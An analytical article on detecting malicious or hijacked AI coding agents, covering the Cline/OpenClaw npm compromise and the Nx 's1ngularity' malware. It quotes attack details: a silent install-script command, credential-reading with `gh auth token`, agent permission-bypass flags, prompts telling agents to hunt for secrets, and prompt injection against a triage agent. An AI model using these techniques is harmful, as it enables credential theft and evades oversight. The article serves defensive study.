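# Telling Malicious AI Agents from Legitimate Ones When Both Leave the Same Traces

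## What an AI agent leaves behind and who can see it

An AI agent is software in which a language model repeatedly chooses actions, such as running a command or editing a file, and tools carry them out. The best-known agents on company laptops are coding assistants like Anthropic's Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Cursor. They run with their user's permissions, so they can usually read any file and run any program that the user can. This access also makes them useful to attackers. An attacker can secretly install an agent or take over an approved one, and either can start the same programs and contact the same servers as a legitimate agent. The security team then has to tell malicious agents from legitimate ones using whatever records it keeps.

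Suppose a developer's laptop has a coding agent that the employer has approved and the publisher has digitally signed. In the morning, the developer opens a terminal, starts the agent and asks it to fix a failing test. In the evening, an attacker who has already got into the developer's account starts the same agent and asks it to collect passwords and access keys. Both runs would leave traces that are ordinary for such tools.

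| Trace | Developer's run | Attacker's run |
|---|---|---|
| Agent process | The signed program, started from a terminal | The same signed program, started from a script |
| Child processes | Command shells, git, a test runner | Command shells, git, a file search |
| File access | Reads source code and settings; writes corrected code | Reads source code and settings, including files that hold keys; writes a list of what it found |
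| Connections | Encrypted, to the model provider | Encrypted, to the model provider |
| API calls (requests to the model service) | Under the developer's account | Under the developer's account |

Almost everything in the attacker's column would look normal in the developer's. Developers also start agents from scripts. Tests often fail because of a bad setting, so the developer's morning run may well open the same file of keys. The clearest difference is the request itself, which the table does not show.

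### What makes something an agent

*Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026), a study of agents that employees run without approval, defines an agent as software that meets three conditions. It connects to a language model, either over the internet or on the same machine. It runs a loop that turns the model's output into actions. It also has tools that act on its surroundings, such as a command shell, the file system or a browser. This definition covers commercial coding assistants and home-made scripts of a few dozen lines that meet the conditions, but not chatbots that only answer questions.

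The traces an agent leaves depend on how it is built, which makes detection harder for defenders. On one workstation, Canale and Soulis found Claude Code in every layer of evidence they examined: a recognisable program file, the shells it had started, a connection to Anthropic's addresses, an editor extension, configuration folders and a history folder. A short Python script that reproduced its behaviour left only a connection and a shell. The script's process ran under the name python.exe, like any other Python program.

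Their detector also has to use a narrower test than the definition. It looks for a process that communicates with a model and has a shell among its descendants. This test misses agents that edit files or make web requests from inside their own process, because they start no shell.

### The machine, the network and the provider

Defenders can watch an agent from the machine it runs on, from the network it uses, or from the company that supplies the model.

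The most detailed traces are on the machine itself. Security people call a laptop or server an endpoint, and endpoint telemetry is its record of processes started, files touched and connections opened. On Windows, one source is Sysmon, a logging component documented in Microsoft's *Understanding Sysmon events*. When a process starts, Sysmon logs its full command line, its parent process and a cryptographic hash that identifies the program file. It also logs DNS queries, which look up the network address for a name such as api.anthropic.com, and the process that made each query. It can log network connections too, but this is off by default because of the volume. Sysmon logs when a file is created, overwritten or deleted, but not when a program only opens and reads it. That gap matters because the attacker's run consists mostly of reading files.

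Endpoint detection and response (EDR) products can block a process that Sysmon would only log. OMB's *Improving Detection of Cybersecurity Vulnerabilities and Incidents on Federal Government Systems* (2021), a memorandum from the White House budget office, defines EDR as continuous real-time monitoring and collection of endpoint data, combined with rule-based automated response and analysis. Microsoft (2026) expects security teams to use this same familiar data to investigate agents' file access and network behaviour. However, according to Microsoft's Sysmon documentation, no single event indicates malicious activity by itself.

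The most promising lead in the example is process ancestry, the chain of parent processes that led to the agent. The developer's agent was started from a terminal and the attacker's from a script. But a missing terminal is weak evidence of an attack, because a legitimate background session's ancestry may not lead back to the terminal where the developer typed the request. According to Anthropic's network documentation, Claude Code's background sessions run under a supervisor process that serves every terminal and keeps running after the one that started it closes. Agents inside virtual machines or containers are even harder to trace, because their processes and connections are invisible from the host system.

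Some agents also write their own log, which comes closer to showing the missing request. According to Anthropic's monitoring documentation, Claude Code can export a record of each prompt, model request and tool result to the employer's systems. The record includes the source of each permission, so an analyst can separate an action that a user approved from one that a standing setting allowed. The record is less useful against the evening intruder. Claude Code blanks out the text of prompts unless an administrator or user chooses to include it. It also attributes actions to the signed-in account, so the attacker's run would appear as the developer's work. If the agent runs on a bare API key instead of an account, the log identifies only the installation and the session, unless the employer adds a name. Whoever controls the developer's settings can also switch the export off, unless the employer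 has locked that setting centrally.

A defender learns much less from the network. The connection to the model provider uses TLS, the encryption behind ordinary secure websites, so a monitor on the company network records the destination, timing and volume of data, but not which process opened the connection. Canale and Soulis point out that an unapproved script and an approved application look the same in network records if they call the same provider. The monitor may not cover a laptop used at home, and a model running on the laptop itself produces no outside traffic. Even the destination is unreliable evidence, because Claude Code's model traffic goes to Amazon, Google or Microsoft when a company buys the model through their clouds, and other agents use resellers whose names hide the provider.

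Encrypted traffic can still help identify the agent that produced it. Canale and Soulis cite a system called AgentPrint, which does this with an F1-score of 0.866 (a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms, where 1 is perfect). This could help find an unknown agent, but it would do little to distinguish the two runs on the laptop above, because both use the same agent.

A company can recover much of the missing detail by putting software on the laptop. Microsoft's Global Secure Access, a service that routes and inspects internet traffic, ties an agent's connections to a user, a device and a process. It requires a client program on the laptop, which makes it partly an endpoint monitor, and TLS inspection, in which the company's equipment decrypts traffic to check it.

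The provider has the best view of what the agent was asked to do. Each turn of the loop passes through its servers, so it receives the prompt, produces the next action and receives the result, including the text of files the agent has passed to the model. It also knows which account or key was used for the request. Some providers classify what they receive. When Anthropic's model refuses a request, the reply can include a category such as "cyber", which Claude Code can send to the employer's logs.

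The provider cannot see what happens on the laptop, so it cannot tell from the account alone whether the developer or an intruder wrote the prompt, which program launched the agent, or whether the machine's owner agreed to install it. The employer can get the provider's records only for accounts it controls. For example, Anthropic lets customers on its Enterprise plan retrieve session transcripts on request for Cowork, the agent mode of Claude's desktop app. If an attacker runs the agent with their own API key, the employer has no account whose records it can request.

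### Covert agents, hijacked agents and malware that calls a model

How useful each of these records is depends on what the attacker has done. A covert agent is one that somebody has put on a machine without its user or owner knowing. The software may be genuine, signed and popular, and it may do nothing objectionable for weeks. Investigators can then learn more from its install origin than from its behaviour. Install origin means how, when and by which process or person the agent was installed. Most of that evidence is on the endpoint, and little of it is available from the network or the provider.

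A hijacked agent has a legitimate install origin. The organisation approved the software and the developer installed it, but the agent is now following an attacker's instructions. The US standards institute NIST uses "agent hijacking" for one common route, in which an attacker plants instructions in data the agent will read, such as a web page or a document. In the evening run on the laptop, the attacker prompts the agent directly. In both cases the evidence is in the instructions and in the difference between what the user wanted and what the agent did. Process ancestry is even less useful when the instructions were hidden in a web page, because the developer did start the agent.

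Conventional malware can also use an AI service without being an agent. A malicious program might ask a model for a piece of text, or use the service's servers only to pass messages to its operator. There may be no loop and no model choosing actions. A network monitor would record a connection to a reputable company, so investigators need to know which process made it and whether that process has a legitimate reason to use an AI service. If attackers use a model only on their own computers, the victim's records may hold no trace of it. *AI Security Report 2026* (2026), from the security company Sophos, notes that AI assistance is invisible in telemetry in many incidents.

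Defenders faced this problem well before AI agents. In living off the land (LOTL), attackers use legitimate tools already on the machine instead of bringing their own malware. CISA's *Identifying and Mitigating LOTL* (2024), a joint guide by security agencies from five countries, including the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), describes the practice. Administrators use the same tools every day, and security software trusts the tools' file hashes and signatures. Many organisations also lack a baseline of normal use, and some endpoint detection and response products may let the tools pass because vendors assume they are safe or because customers asked for an exception. The guide also warns about remote-administration software, which can run commands on every computer in a network. A coding agent is quite similar to that software, except that it takes instructions in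 plain English. The technique is common. The Hacker News (2026) reports that, by the security company CrowdStrike's count, 82 percent of its 2025 detections involved no malware. Detecting misuse of built-in tools is now a research field of its own, and its methods and its trouble with false alarms both carry over to agents.

### Is it an agent, is it authorised, is it harmful?

Much confusion about monitoring comes from treating these questions as one. Microsoft sells a separate product for each, which makes the differences easy to see.

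Microsoft's Defender security product finds agents by matching them against a list of known ones, which doesn't include home-made scripts with no product name. Microsoft counts each combination of user, device and agent type as one agent, so Claude Code running in 15 project folders for one user on one laptop appears as a single inventory entry. Under that rule, the developer's run and the attacker's run also share an entry. The entry includes useful context, such as when Defender first detected the agent and whether the agent approves its own actions automatically. But Microsoft offers this as a discovery tool, without alerts.

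Authorisation, by contrast, depends on a decision that somebody in the organisation made. Canale and Soulis call it a property of identity and policy rather than behaviour. Global Secure Access treats an agent as managed if the company has registered it in Microsoft's identity system, and as a "shadow" agent if not. If the coding agent on the laptop is registered, the attacker's run of it also counts as managed. Stronger proof of identity, such as attestation (in which another party checks evidence of what software is running), would confirm that the program is genuine, but the attacker's copy is genuine too.

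Neither of the other answers establishes whether an agent is doing harm. Employees install unapproved agents to get their work done, usually with no ill intent, and an approved agent can leak a company's keys. The agent's behaviour is also a poor guide. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* (2026) reports that the company's behavioural engine cannot distinguish some activity by legitimate coding agents from an intruder's. Sophos' *Fake AI, real malware* (2026) reviewed 86 cases that analysts had tagged for AI involvement over a year, and confirmed 34 as adversarial. Another 25 were harmless developer tools that had set off behavioural alarms, and in the remaining 27 an AI keyword appeared only incidentally. All of these cases had already reached human analysts, so they are weak evidence of the mix on an ordinary laptop.

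Microsoft's runtime protection tries to detect harm by inspecting the content of a user's prompt, each tool call before the agent makes it, and each response that comes back. It can block the agent if it finds injected instructions. This is the right content to check for signs that an agent has been hijacked, but for now the protection supports only Claude Code and GitHub's command-line Copilot. It also looks for instructions hidden in otherwise legitimate content. An attacker who openly types "find the access keys" has hidden nothing, and a developer cleaning up a project might type the same words.

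For any particular incident, it helps to ask which trace differed, who could see it, and how soon. On the imaginary laptop, the parent process differed. The employer's EDR product could record that at once, but a script is such a common parent process that probably nobody would look. The prompt differed much more. The provider received it immediately but had no reason to doubt the account. The employer could have read it only if it had arranged beforehand to export prompt text. Anthropic's *Monitor Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* describes Cowork's export as a real-time stream, so the prompt could reach an analyst while the agent is still working. A transcript requested the next morning would contain the same prompt, but the keys would already be gone.

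## An agent installed without consent: Cline and OpenClaw, February 2026

On 17 February 2026, somebody used a stolen credential to publish a new version of Cline, an AI coding assistant. For about eight hours, people who installed that version also got a second agent, OpenClaw, which they had not asked for. OpenClaw is genuine and popular software, so nothing about the program itself could show that it was unwanted, only how it had been installed.

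### Eight hours on npm

Developers get Cline's command-line edition from npm, the main public registry of JavaScript packages. The stolen credential was an npm publishing token, which works like a password for releasing new versions of a package. Cline lost it through an AI agent it had set up in December 2025 to sort incoming bug reports. An outsider could manipulate that agent to reach the system that held the publishing credentials. *Clinejection* (Khan, 2026) states that the researcher's private report of 1 January and several follow-ups had no effect until the findings went public on 9 February.

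Cline then removed the automation within 30 minutes and began replacing its credentials, but it deleted the wrong npm token. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) explains that staff checked the deletion on an npm management page, which showed no active tokens although the stolen one still worked. On 10 February an anonymous emailer told Khan that they held valid Cline credentials. Khan forwarded the message to Cline, which replied the next day that it had revoked everything. Six days later, somebody used the stolen token to publish cline 2.3.0.

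Version 2.3.0 appeared at 3:26 am Pacific time. Only package.json, the file that describes the package to npm, differed from the previous release, 2.2.3. It had a new version number and one added install script, which npm runs automatically when it installs the package. The script ran `npm install -g openclaw@latest`, which fetches the newest OpenClaw and installs it for use from any folder. Cline published a clean version, 2.4.0, at 11:23 am and marked 2.3.0 as deprecated a few minutes later.

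*Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected* (Likhith, 2026) puts the number of downloads at about 4,000, which is close to normal traffic. Cline usually gets about 90,000 downloads a week, or some 4,300 in eight hours, according to *Compromised npm package silently installs OpenClaw on developer machines* (CSO Online, 2026). The attacker did not have to lure anyone, because routine installations and updates downloaded the compromised package. Probably fewer than 4,000 people were affected, since automated build servers download packages too.

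### Was OpenClaw ever running?

OpenClaw runs on the user's own computer and connects to chat apps such as WhatsApp, Telegram and Slack. It can read email, browse the web and run programs. According to its security documentation, OpenClaw is designed to run commands without asking for approval by default on a machine with one trusted operator. It also stores credentials and session transcripts in a folder on the machine.

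An agent with those permissions could do great harm if an attacker controlled it, but it would have to be running first, and accounts differ on whether it was. Likhith describes a background service, called the Gateway, that survives reboots and gives an attacker a lasting foothold. This is a fair description of OpenClaw after setup, but the command in the Cline script is only the first step in OpenClaw's installation instructions, and a separate onboarding command installs the service. Plate (2026), in *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw*, states that the compromised release did not install or start the Gateway. Sarah Gooding of the security company Socket, quoted by CSO Online, likewise found that "nothing ran automatically beyond the install".

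The second account is almost certainly right. Onboarding also checks OpenClaw's access to a model and configures the Gateway, so a fresh copy from the Cline script had no working connection to a model and no channel for instructions. npm may have run some of OpenClaw's setup code, since OpenClaw's current instructions tell users to allow the package's install scripts, but that is still part of installation. Likhith also mentions a critical flaw in versions before 2026.1.29 that let outsiders take control of a Gateway, but the Cline script fetched the latest version.

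Some Cline users, however, presumably already had OpenClaw, and on their machines the script would have updated a copy that they had chosen to install and might have been running.

Everyone else was left with a dormant agent. An intruder who got in later by another route could still have used it, much as malware in the Nx attack of August 2025 used agents already on developers' machines. No account reports that anyone did this, and Plate saw no need for victims to change their passwords or keys.

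Nobody has established who published the release or why. Plate thinks it resembles a prank more than a serious attack. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, traces the theft to a since-deleted GitHub account that had also probed another company's test project. He finds the evidence consistent with a security researcher's demonstration. The email to Khan would fit that explanation, as a warning that Cline failed to act on, but nobody has shown that the emailer and the publisher were the same person. The attacker could have installed anything, and the harmless payload is weak evidence of harmless intent.

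### Why scanning the files did not help

A file scanner compares files with known malware or searches them for suspicious code, and here there was almost nothing for it to find. Cline's program file had the same cryptographic hash as the one in version 2.2.3, so the two files were identical. OpenClaw came from its developers' own package. The only added line was a command that every new user who follows OpenClaw's instructions types.

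A counterfeit agent is easier to detect than a genuine one installed without consent, because a scanner can examine the malicious code itself. JFrog's *GhostClaw Unmasked* describes a malicious npm package that posed as an OpenClaw installer. Its install script runs a global npm installation, much like the line in cline 2.3.0, but the program it installs is an obfuscated dropper, meaning deliberately unreadable code that brings in further malware.

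Scanners can also match a bad release by name once someone has listed it. OSV, a public database of problems in open-source software, has two entries for cline 2.3.0. OSV's *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026) rates the severity as low and calls OpenClaw legitimate, while OSV's *MAL-2026-1380* (2026) lists the Cline release as malicious code. Both are reasonable, because the release ran a command that Cline had not authorised, but the software it fetched was harmless in itself. Both entries date from 19 February, two days after the release, so a scanner that relied on them could not have matched it before then.

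### How monitors caught the release

StepSecurity, the company behind Likhith's account, runs a service that watches npm for unusual releases. It flagged cline 2.3.0 after 14 minutes, without needing access to any victim's computer.

The main clue was that an ordinary user account had published version 2.3.0. Cline had been using trusted publishing, in which npm accepts a short-lived credential from a project's automated build system instead of a stored token. The release also lacked a provenance attestation, a signed statement that links a package to its source code and the build that produced it. A thief with only a publishing token can release a package but cannot produce a statement tying it to Cline's build system. The install script was another warning sign, because Cline had not had one before. Plate reports that Endor Labs' scanner detected the same changes by comparing the release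 with an earlier one.

The accounts differ on how unusual the missing attestation was. Likhith says all earlier legitimate releases came through trusted publishing. But Cline wrote in its post-mortem that versions from 2.4.0 "now include" attestations, and Plate's example of an attested release is a nightly test build. If some ordinary releases had lacked attestations, the missing one on 2.3.0 was weaker evidence than Likhith suggests, and the install script mattered more.

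Attestations help only if somebody checks them. Cline had turned on trusted publishing but, as far as Plate could tell, had left the older token route open, so npm accepted the unattested release. Plate considers manual checks practical only for packages a developer installs directly, since those can bring in hundreds or thousands of others. A valid attestation doesn't guarantee safety either. Gooding (2026), in *npm v12 Ships With Install Scripts Off by Default*, notes that other attackers have published malicious packages through projects' legitimate build systems, some with valid provenance.

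The release stayed on npm for nearly eight hours, even though it was caught within minutes. A waiting period would have protected more people. StepSecurity sells a check that rejects project changes introducing package versions less than two days old, and pnpm, an alternative to npm's installer, now requires versions to be at least 24 hours old by default. Either wait would have outlasted the incident, though it would also delay urgent fixes.

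### What a victim's own security software would have recorded

On an affected laptop, an EDR product with ordinary process logging would have recorded npm installing Cline, then a command shell, then a second npm process installing OpenClaw. It would also have recorded a connection to the npm registry and new files in npm's global package folder. A developer who wanted OpenClaw would have typed the same command and got the same files.

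The process ancestry would have differed from that of a deliberate installation, in which the npm command comes from a terminal or from a setup script that somebody chose to run. In the Cline case, it came from another package's install script. The EDR product could record this immediately, but an analyst would have needed a reason to look, because install scripts often start other programs. Gooding lists several well-known packages that compile code during installation, and others, such as the browser-testing tools Playwright and Puppeteer, that download large programs. An alert whenever npm starts a shell would fire too often to be useful on a developer's machine. A rule for install scripts that install a different package globally would probably produce far fewer false alarms, but somebody would have had to write it beforehand.

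The Hacker News reports that Microsoft's threat intelligence team saw a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day because of the Cline compromise. Microsoft can count installations across a very large number of machines, whereas a single employer might have had only one or two. CSO Online cites an estimate of 720,000 OpenClaw downloads a week, or about 100,000 a day, so the Cline release would have accounted for only around 4 percent of a typical day's downloads. An analyst who knew only that OpenClaw had appeared on a laptop would have had good reason to assume the laptop's user wanted it.

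The evidence also gets worse with time. Updating Cline replaces version 2.3.0 but leaves OpenClaw installed, so a user who only updates Cline removes the most obvious clue to where OpenClaw came from. The employer then depends on stored process records. eeNews Europe's *OpenClaw scanner targets AI agent exposure with endpoint detection* describes a scanner from Astrix that uses such records. The scanner searches EDR data for OpenClaw and reports the user and device, but it does not show whether that user agreed to the installation.

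A missing workspace is another clue. OpenClaw creates one for the agent during onboarding, so a copy without one has probably never been used. An unused copy could belong to a Cline victim, but also to a developer who installed OpenClaw out of curiosity and then lost interest.

### Should security products block OpenClaw?

David Shipley of Beauceron Security told CSO Online that the attackers had "effectively turned OpenClaw into malware" that EDR would not stop. He argues that attacks of this kind will succeed unless security companies class OpenClaw as malware or as a potentially unwanted application (PUA). Sophos' support pages define PUAs as programs that are not malicious by design but may be unsuitable for a device, and users can allow them.

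Sophos' *The OpenClaw experiment is a warning shot for enterprise AI security* (2026), published four days before the Cline release, already described a PUA protection for OpenClaw and searches for the agent on customers' machines.

The main objection is that many people installed OpenClaw on purpose. Bitdefender's *Technical Advisory* (2026) describes its spread from personal experiments into corporate networks, and Microsoft has seen it in company pilots. Blocking it everywhere would break work that depends on it, and Shipley accepts that a company in this position has no good option. It is also hard to say which property of OpenClaw justifies the label. If it is the ability to run commands and edit files, the label fits Cline too. Microsoft's criticism that OpenClaw has few built-in security controls is a better reason to single it out, but it applies equally to copies that people chose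 to install.

The label is still useful to an employer that prohibits OpenClaw, because its security product can block or report every copy, including those from the Cline release, without investigating where each one came from. An employer that permits OpenClaw would have to allow it in the security product, which would then also allow the copies installed covertly. Both employers still need to know how a copy was installed to decide what to do next, because an employee who ignored a software policy calls for a very different response than a compromised package does.

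### Approved software on a developer's machine

Application allowlisting goes further by blocking every program the organisation has not approved, whether or not it is harmful. Some organisations instead keep an approved-software list of what employees may install, and remove anything else they find. Avanet's *Configure Sophos Endpoint Application Control* distinguishes this kind of control, which enforces the organisation's decision about which applications it wants, from malware protection.

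Allowlisting is in principle the right defence against a covert agent, because the attacker gains nothing by choosing reputable software. An allowlist that covered npm packages and omitted OpenClaw would have stopped the unwanted copies from running. But a list of executable files could easily have missed them. OpenClaw runs on Node.js, the standard program for running JavaScript outside a browser. Developers who use npm need Node.js, so it would be on the list, and a control that checks only the executable would allow any JavaScript that Node.js ran.

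Blocking by network address has a similar weakness. Jamf, which makes management software for Apple devices, has added OpenClaw domains such as openclaw.ai to a category that customers can block. But the Cline script fetched OpenClaw from the npm registry, which is hard to block because developers need it. Jamf recommends combining several controls, including blocks on execution, endpoint monitoring and automatic removal, because none is sufficient alone.

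Strict lists of approved programs suit a payroll clerk's computer much better than a programmer's. Programmers install unfamiliar packages for their work, and each build of their own software may produce a program that isn't on any list. Avanet advises administrators to observe what people use and run a pilot before blocking anything. Sophos expects most organisations with reasonably mature controls to be able to block OpenClaw. That is plausible for one well-known product, but blocking OpenClaw would not help if the next attacker chose a different agent.

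npm has since adopted a narrower form of allowlisting that suits developers better. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) announced that npm would stop running packages' install scripts unless the user had approved them, and version 12 made this the default in July 2026. It would probably have prevented the Cline incident. Cline had no earlier install script for anyone to approve, so npm would have skipped the new one, printed a warning and installed Cline as usual.

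The new default still relies on people approving scripts sensibly. Gooding notes that npm's review command shows what each script will run, but not what files it will fetch or whether it will contact the network. The Cline script was unusually easy to read. The protection is also weaker for packages whose scripts a user has already approved, and attackers would now prefer to compromise those packages.

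### An agent built for the purpose

An attacker who writes a new agent gives up the advantage of using reputable software. Rogue Authority's *Built for an AI at the controls* (2026), an analysis that Anthropic's Claude produced in November, examines a Windows program named Remote AI Agent. The program takes screenshots, clicks, types and runs PowerShell commands on instructions from a remote server. A legitimate agent that operates a desktop does much the same, so those actions alone would be poor evidence that the program is malicious.

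The rest of the program is much easier to identify. It has no digital signature. It sets itself to start at login under its own name and contacts a fixed domain that also hosts a control panel for guessing remote-desktop passwords. It also opens a window with a notice that remote control is active. Defenders can search for any of these features, and an allowlist would block the program even if defenders didn't know about them.

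It is less certain that the program is an AI agent. The server rejected its registration during the analysis, so it received no instructions, and the program contains no reference to a model. An ordinary script could be sending the commands. If a model chooses them, the victim's computer reaches it only through the attacker's server and never contacts an AI provider. Canale and Soulis' detector, which relies on contact with a model, could therefore miss this program.

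That detector would have missed the dormant OpenClaw copies too, because they contacted no model and started no shell. A model provider would have had no record of them, and a network monitor would have recorded only a download from a registry that developers use routinely. The install origin was the trace that differed. Registry monitors could detect the suspicious release within 14 minutes from public data. The employer's EDR product could record in real time which script installed OpenClaw, but most employers had little reason to check until Cline or a security company told them about the release.

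## An approved agent used by malware: the Nx attack, August 2025

The malware in the Nx attack looked for AI agents that developers had already installed and told them to search for secrets. In the Cline incident, the warning sign was how OpenClaw reached the machine. The agents in the Nx attack had been installed normally, so any warning had to come from how the malware started them and what it did with the results.

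Nx is a tool for building and testing large software projects, and developers download it from npm several million times a week. On 26 August 2025, an attacker used a stolen npm publishing token to release malicious versions of Nx and some related packages. *S1ngularity*, Strumpflohner's account of the attack for the Nx team, traces the theft to an automated check on the titles of proposed code changes. An outsider submitted a change with shell commands in its title, and Nx's build system ran them. The attack became known as s1ngularity, after the name of the repositories where the malware published victims' data.

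### What the install script did

The malicious versions of Nx contained an install script called telemetry.js. On Windows the script quit at once. On macOS and Linux it collected environment variables, which often hold access keys, and the user's npm and GitHub tokens. This required no AI; the script got the GitHub token, for example, by running `gh auth token`, a command in GitHub's own command-line tool that prints the signed-in user's credential.

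The script also looked for three coding agents: Anthropic's Claude Code, Google's Gemini CLI and Amazon Q. It started each one it found with a prompt and a permission-bypass flag, a launch option that lets an agent act without asking its user to approve each step. The prompt told the agent to find files that might be sensitive and write a list of their locations. The code in Snyk's *Weaponizing AI Coding Agents for Malware in the Nx Malicious Package* (2025) shows that the install script itself then read every file on the list. It encoded the contents and uploaded them to a new public repository in the victim's GitHub account.

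Malware doesn't need AI to search for files. An analysis of the leaked data by the cloud security company Wiz, *s1ngularity's Aftermath*, suggests that using an agent makes malware more flexible and may help it avoid detection, but also gives it more ways to fail.

Accounts differ on how long the malicious releases were online. Strumpflohner gives four hours, while Snyk gives about five hours and 20 minutes. The timeline in *s1ngularity* (Kurmi, 2025) explains the difference. The first malicious version appeared at 10:32 pm UTC, and npm removed the affected versions of the main package at 2:44 am, a little over four hours later. Snyk's figure matches the time until Nx revoked the compromised account's access at 3:52 am. npm did not remove some of the related packages until 10:20 am.

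### How many victims had an agent, and how often it complied

Wiz found that the malware had publicly leaked the secrets of more than 1,700 users, and Wiz collected data on over a thousand of these cases. The leak included more than 2,000 verified secrets. Over the next few days, attackers used stolen GitHub tokens to make public more than 6,700 private repositories belonging to at least 480 accounts.

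Wiz estimated that about half of the victims had at least one of the three agents. Even with an agent installed, the attack often did not work.

| Agent | Permission-bypass flag | Victims who had it | What stopped it, according to Wiz |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | `--dangerously-skip-permissions` | Most of those with any agent | The model refused almost a quarter of the time; some copies lacked credit, a working login or prior approval for the flag |
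| Gemini CLI | `--yolo` | About 15% | Fewer refusals, but default folder restrictions stopped almost a quarter of runs |
| Amazon Q | `--trust-all-tools` | About 5% | Refusals much like Claude Code's, because Q uses Claude models |

The attacker rewrote the prompt during the attack. In one version, the attacker claimed to have permission for a security test, and Wiz linked that wording to refusals.

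A second count, in *The Nx s1ngularity attack* (2025) by GitGuardian, a company that searches for leaked credentials, found agents on a lower share of the compromised systems, 33 percent. It isn't clear why this share is so much lower than the first. Neither is a good estimate for developers in general, because the malware could publish data only if the victim had GitHub's command-line tool and a working token, and people with that tool may well be more likely to use a coding agent. GitGuardian also reports that of 366 systems where the malware tried to use an agent, only 95 produced the list of files.

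The agents added little to the theft. Wiz reports that they helped steal data in under a quarter of cases. Many searched only Nx's own folder and returned 14 or 15 harmless files. The roughly 20,000 files that leaked through the agents contained fewer than 100 unique valid secrets, so ordinary code in the install script took the great majority of the secrets. But these results describe the agents of August 2025, and current ones are much better at searching.

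### The traces that looked normal

The agent program was the developer's own copy, so its file hash and signature were correct. It ran under the developer's account on the developer's machine and used the developer's login or key for the model service. Its connections went to the usual provider.

The install script uploaded the stolen data to GitHub with the victim's own token, and most victims probably used GitHub every day. Wiz believes the attacker chose this method to avoid setting up any servers. It also meant that defenders had no suspicious domain to block.

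The package was easier to identify as malicious than cline 2.3.0 because it contained the code that stole the data. But for the first few hours nobody had analysed that code, so a victim's employer would have had to notice the behaviour.

### Process ancestry

npm and coding agents often appear in the same chain of processes. A developer asks an agent to add a library, and the agent runs `npm install`. In the Nx attack the order was reversed: npm ran the install script, and the install script started the agent.

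That order is rare in legitimate work. Automated builds run agents, for example to review a code change, but normally as a separate step rather than from inside a package's install script. A package might check whether an agent is present so it can offer to work with it, but it would have little reason to give the agent a task. Ancestry is therefore probably the strongest single clue on the machine, although neither Wiz nor Kurmi measured how often this order occurs in harmless builds.

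A detector would have to look further back than the agent's immediate parent process, Node.js, because Node.js runs many developer tools. Some victims had not typed an installation command. Kurmi explains that Nx Console, an extension for the VS Code editor, downloaded and ran the newest Nx to check its version number. On those machines, the chain of processes began with the editor, which often starts agents for legitimate reasons. If a developer's own agent had installed Nx, the chain would have had an agent at both ends and might have looked like one agent starting a helper. In either case, an analyst would need to find the install script in the middle.

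### Launch flags and the prompt

Permission-bypass flags are weaker evidence. Nobody is present during an automated build to approve each step, so whoever sets it up must either use such a flag or list the permitted actions in advance. Some developers also use the flags on their own laptops because the approval requests are tedious. Alerts on every use would therefore be mostly false positives. The flag is stronger evidence when combined with the process ancestry, because an install script that starts an agent and also removes its need for approval is much harder to explain as legitimate use.

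The absence of a flag doesn't prove much either, because an employer or user can often grant the same permission in the agent's settings, and then nothing unusual appears when the agent starts.

Snyk advises people who have these agents to search their shell history for the flags. This would show whether a developer had typed them, but it would probably miss the malware's use, because shell history records commands entered at the prompt and the install script started the agents directly. Process records from an EDR product are a better place to look.

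Those records could also have contained the attacker's prompt, which would have been more useful than the flag. The malware passed the entire prompt to the agent in the launch command, so an EDR product that kept full command lines would have stored it word for word, even if the agent's own log left it out. Automated builds also pass prompts this way, but usually to request a code review or a fix, not a search of a home folder for cryptocurrency wallets and private keys. Later versions of the Nx prompt were less obvious because they mainly requested configuration and text files, which a developer might also want to find.

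### File access and the upload

The original prompt told the agent to search the user's home folder and several system folders. A search this wide would be unusual in an automated build, where an agent normally works on one project, often in a temporary container. It would be easier to overlook on a laptop, where backup programs and virus scanners read files all over the disk and a developer might ask an agent to find a lost configuration file.

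The search was also hard to record because the agent mostly needed to list file names, which a monitor that logs only changes to files would miss. The install script read the files, so a rule to detect agents opening private keys would not have fired. Where an agent searched only Nx's folder, its file access was narrow.

The list itself was easier to find, because the agent saved it as `/tmp/inventory.txt`. Mondoo's *GHSA-cxm3-wv7p-598c*, a copy of the Nx security advisory, treats that file as proof that the malware had affected the machine. But the install script could still have stolen tokens from a machine without the file. By GitGuardian's count, about three quarters of the systems on which the malware tried to use an agent never produced the file.

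To test whether a monitor could detect the last step, StepSecurity ran one of the malicious releases in an automated build under its own monitoring product, which flagged the calls to GitHub's API during `npm install`. Kurmi argues that legitimate installations should not make such calls. That rule is reasonable for a build whose normal connections are known, but some packages fetch ready-made programs from GitHub as they install. On a developer's laptop, several other programs may also be contacting GitHub at the same moment.

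Creating a new public repository during a package installation is much more unusual than contacting GitHub. However, a network monitor could not tell the two apart unless the employer decrypted the traffic. GitHub could tell them apart, and it recorded the new repository in the security log of the victim's account.

### Similar attacks in 2026

Attackers have since found other ways to misuse approved agents. *How Malicious Plugins Transform AI Agents Into Insider Threats* (Chandran and Kavitha) describes a case that the security company CyberProof investigated. The customer had a well-known, digitally signed coding agent on hundreds of machines. On one, the agent was set to run scripts without asking. Its folder of "skills" (add-ons with instructions and scripts for particular jobs) held a malicious package whose name suggested a routine approval process.

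Its scripts listed the running browsers, read the file where a browser keeps saved passwords, and called the operating system's function for decrypting them. They did this for two different browsers within 15 minutes. Signature checks and allowlisting did not help, because every program involved was legitimate.

The clues from the Nx attack would have been less useful here. The agent started a shell, which started Python, as coding agents routinely do. The EDR product instead flagged the last steps: reading the password file, decrypting its contents and changing memory protections in the Python process. This behaviour is a better clue than a broad file search because very few programming tasks require a user's saved browser passwords.

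Chandran and Kavitha still advise security teams to run their detection rules in report-only mode until the teams know what their own agents normally do. They also recommend saving the agent's prompts and session logs, since process records may not show whether a user, an add-on or a hidden instruction was responsible. At least one of the rules needs correcting. Its description covers reading a browser's password file, but its query matches only files that a program has renamed or modified, so as published it would miss a script that only read the file.

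In December 2026, Microsoft reported another campaign in *ClickFix campaign targets crypto users with AI coding agent* (Patil and Robielos, 2026), which describes attackers who install a malicious browser extension and abuse a legitimate coding agent to steal data. In a ClickFix attack, a web page persuades people to run the attacker's command themselves, usually by presenting it as the fix for some fault. This weakens process ancestry as evidence, because the chain can begin with a command the user typed.

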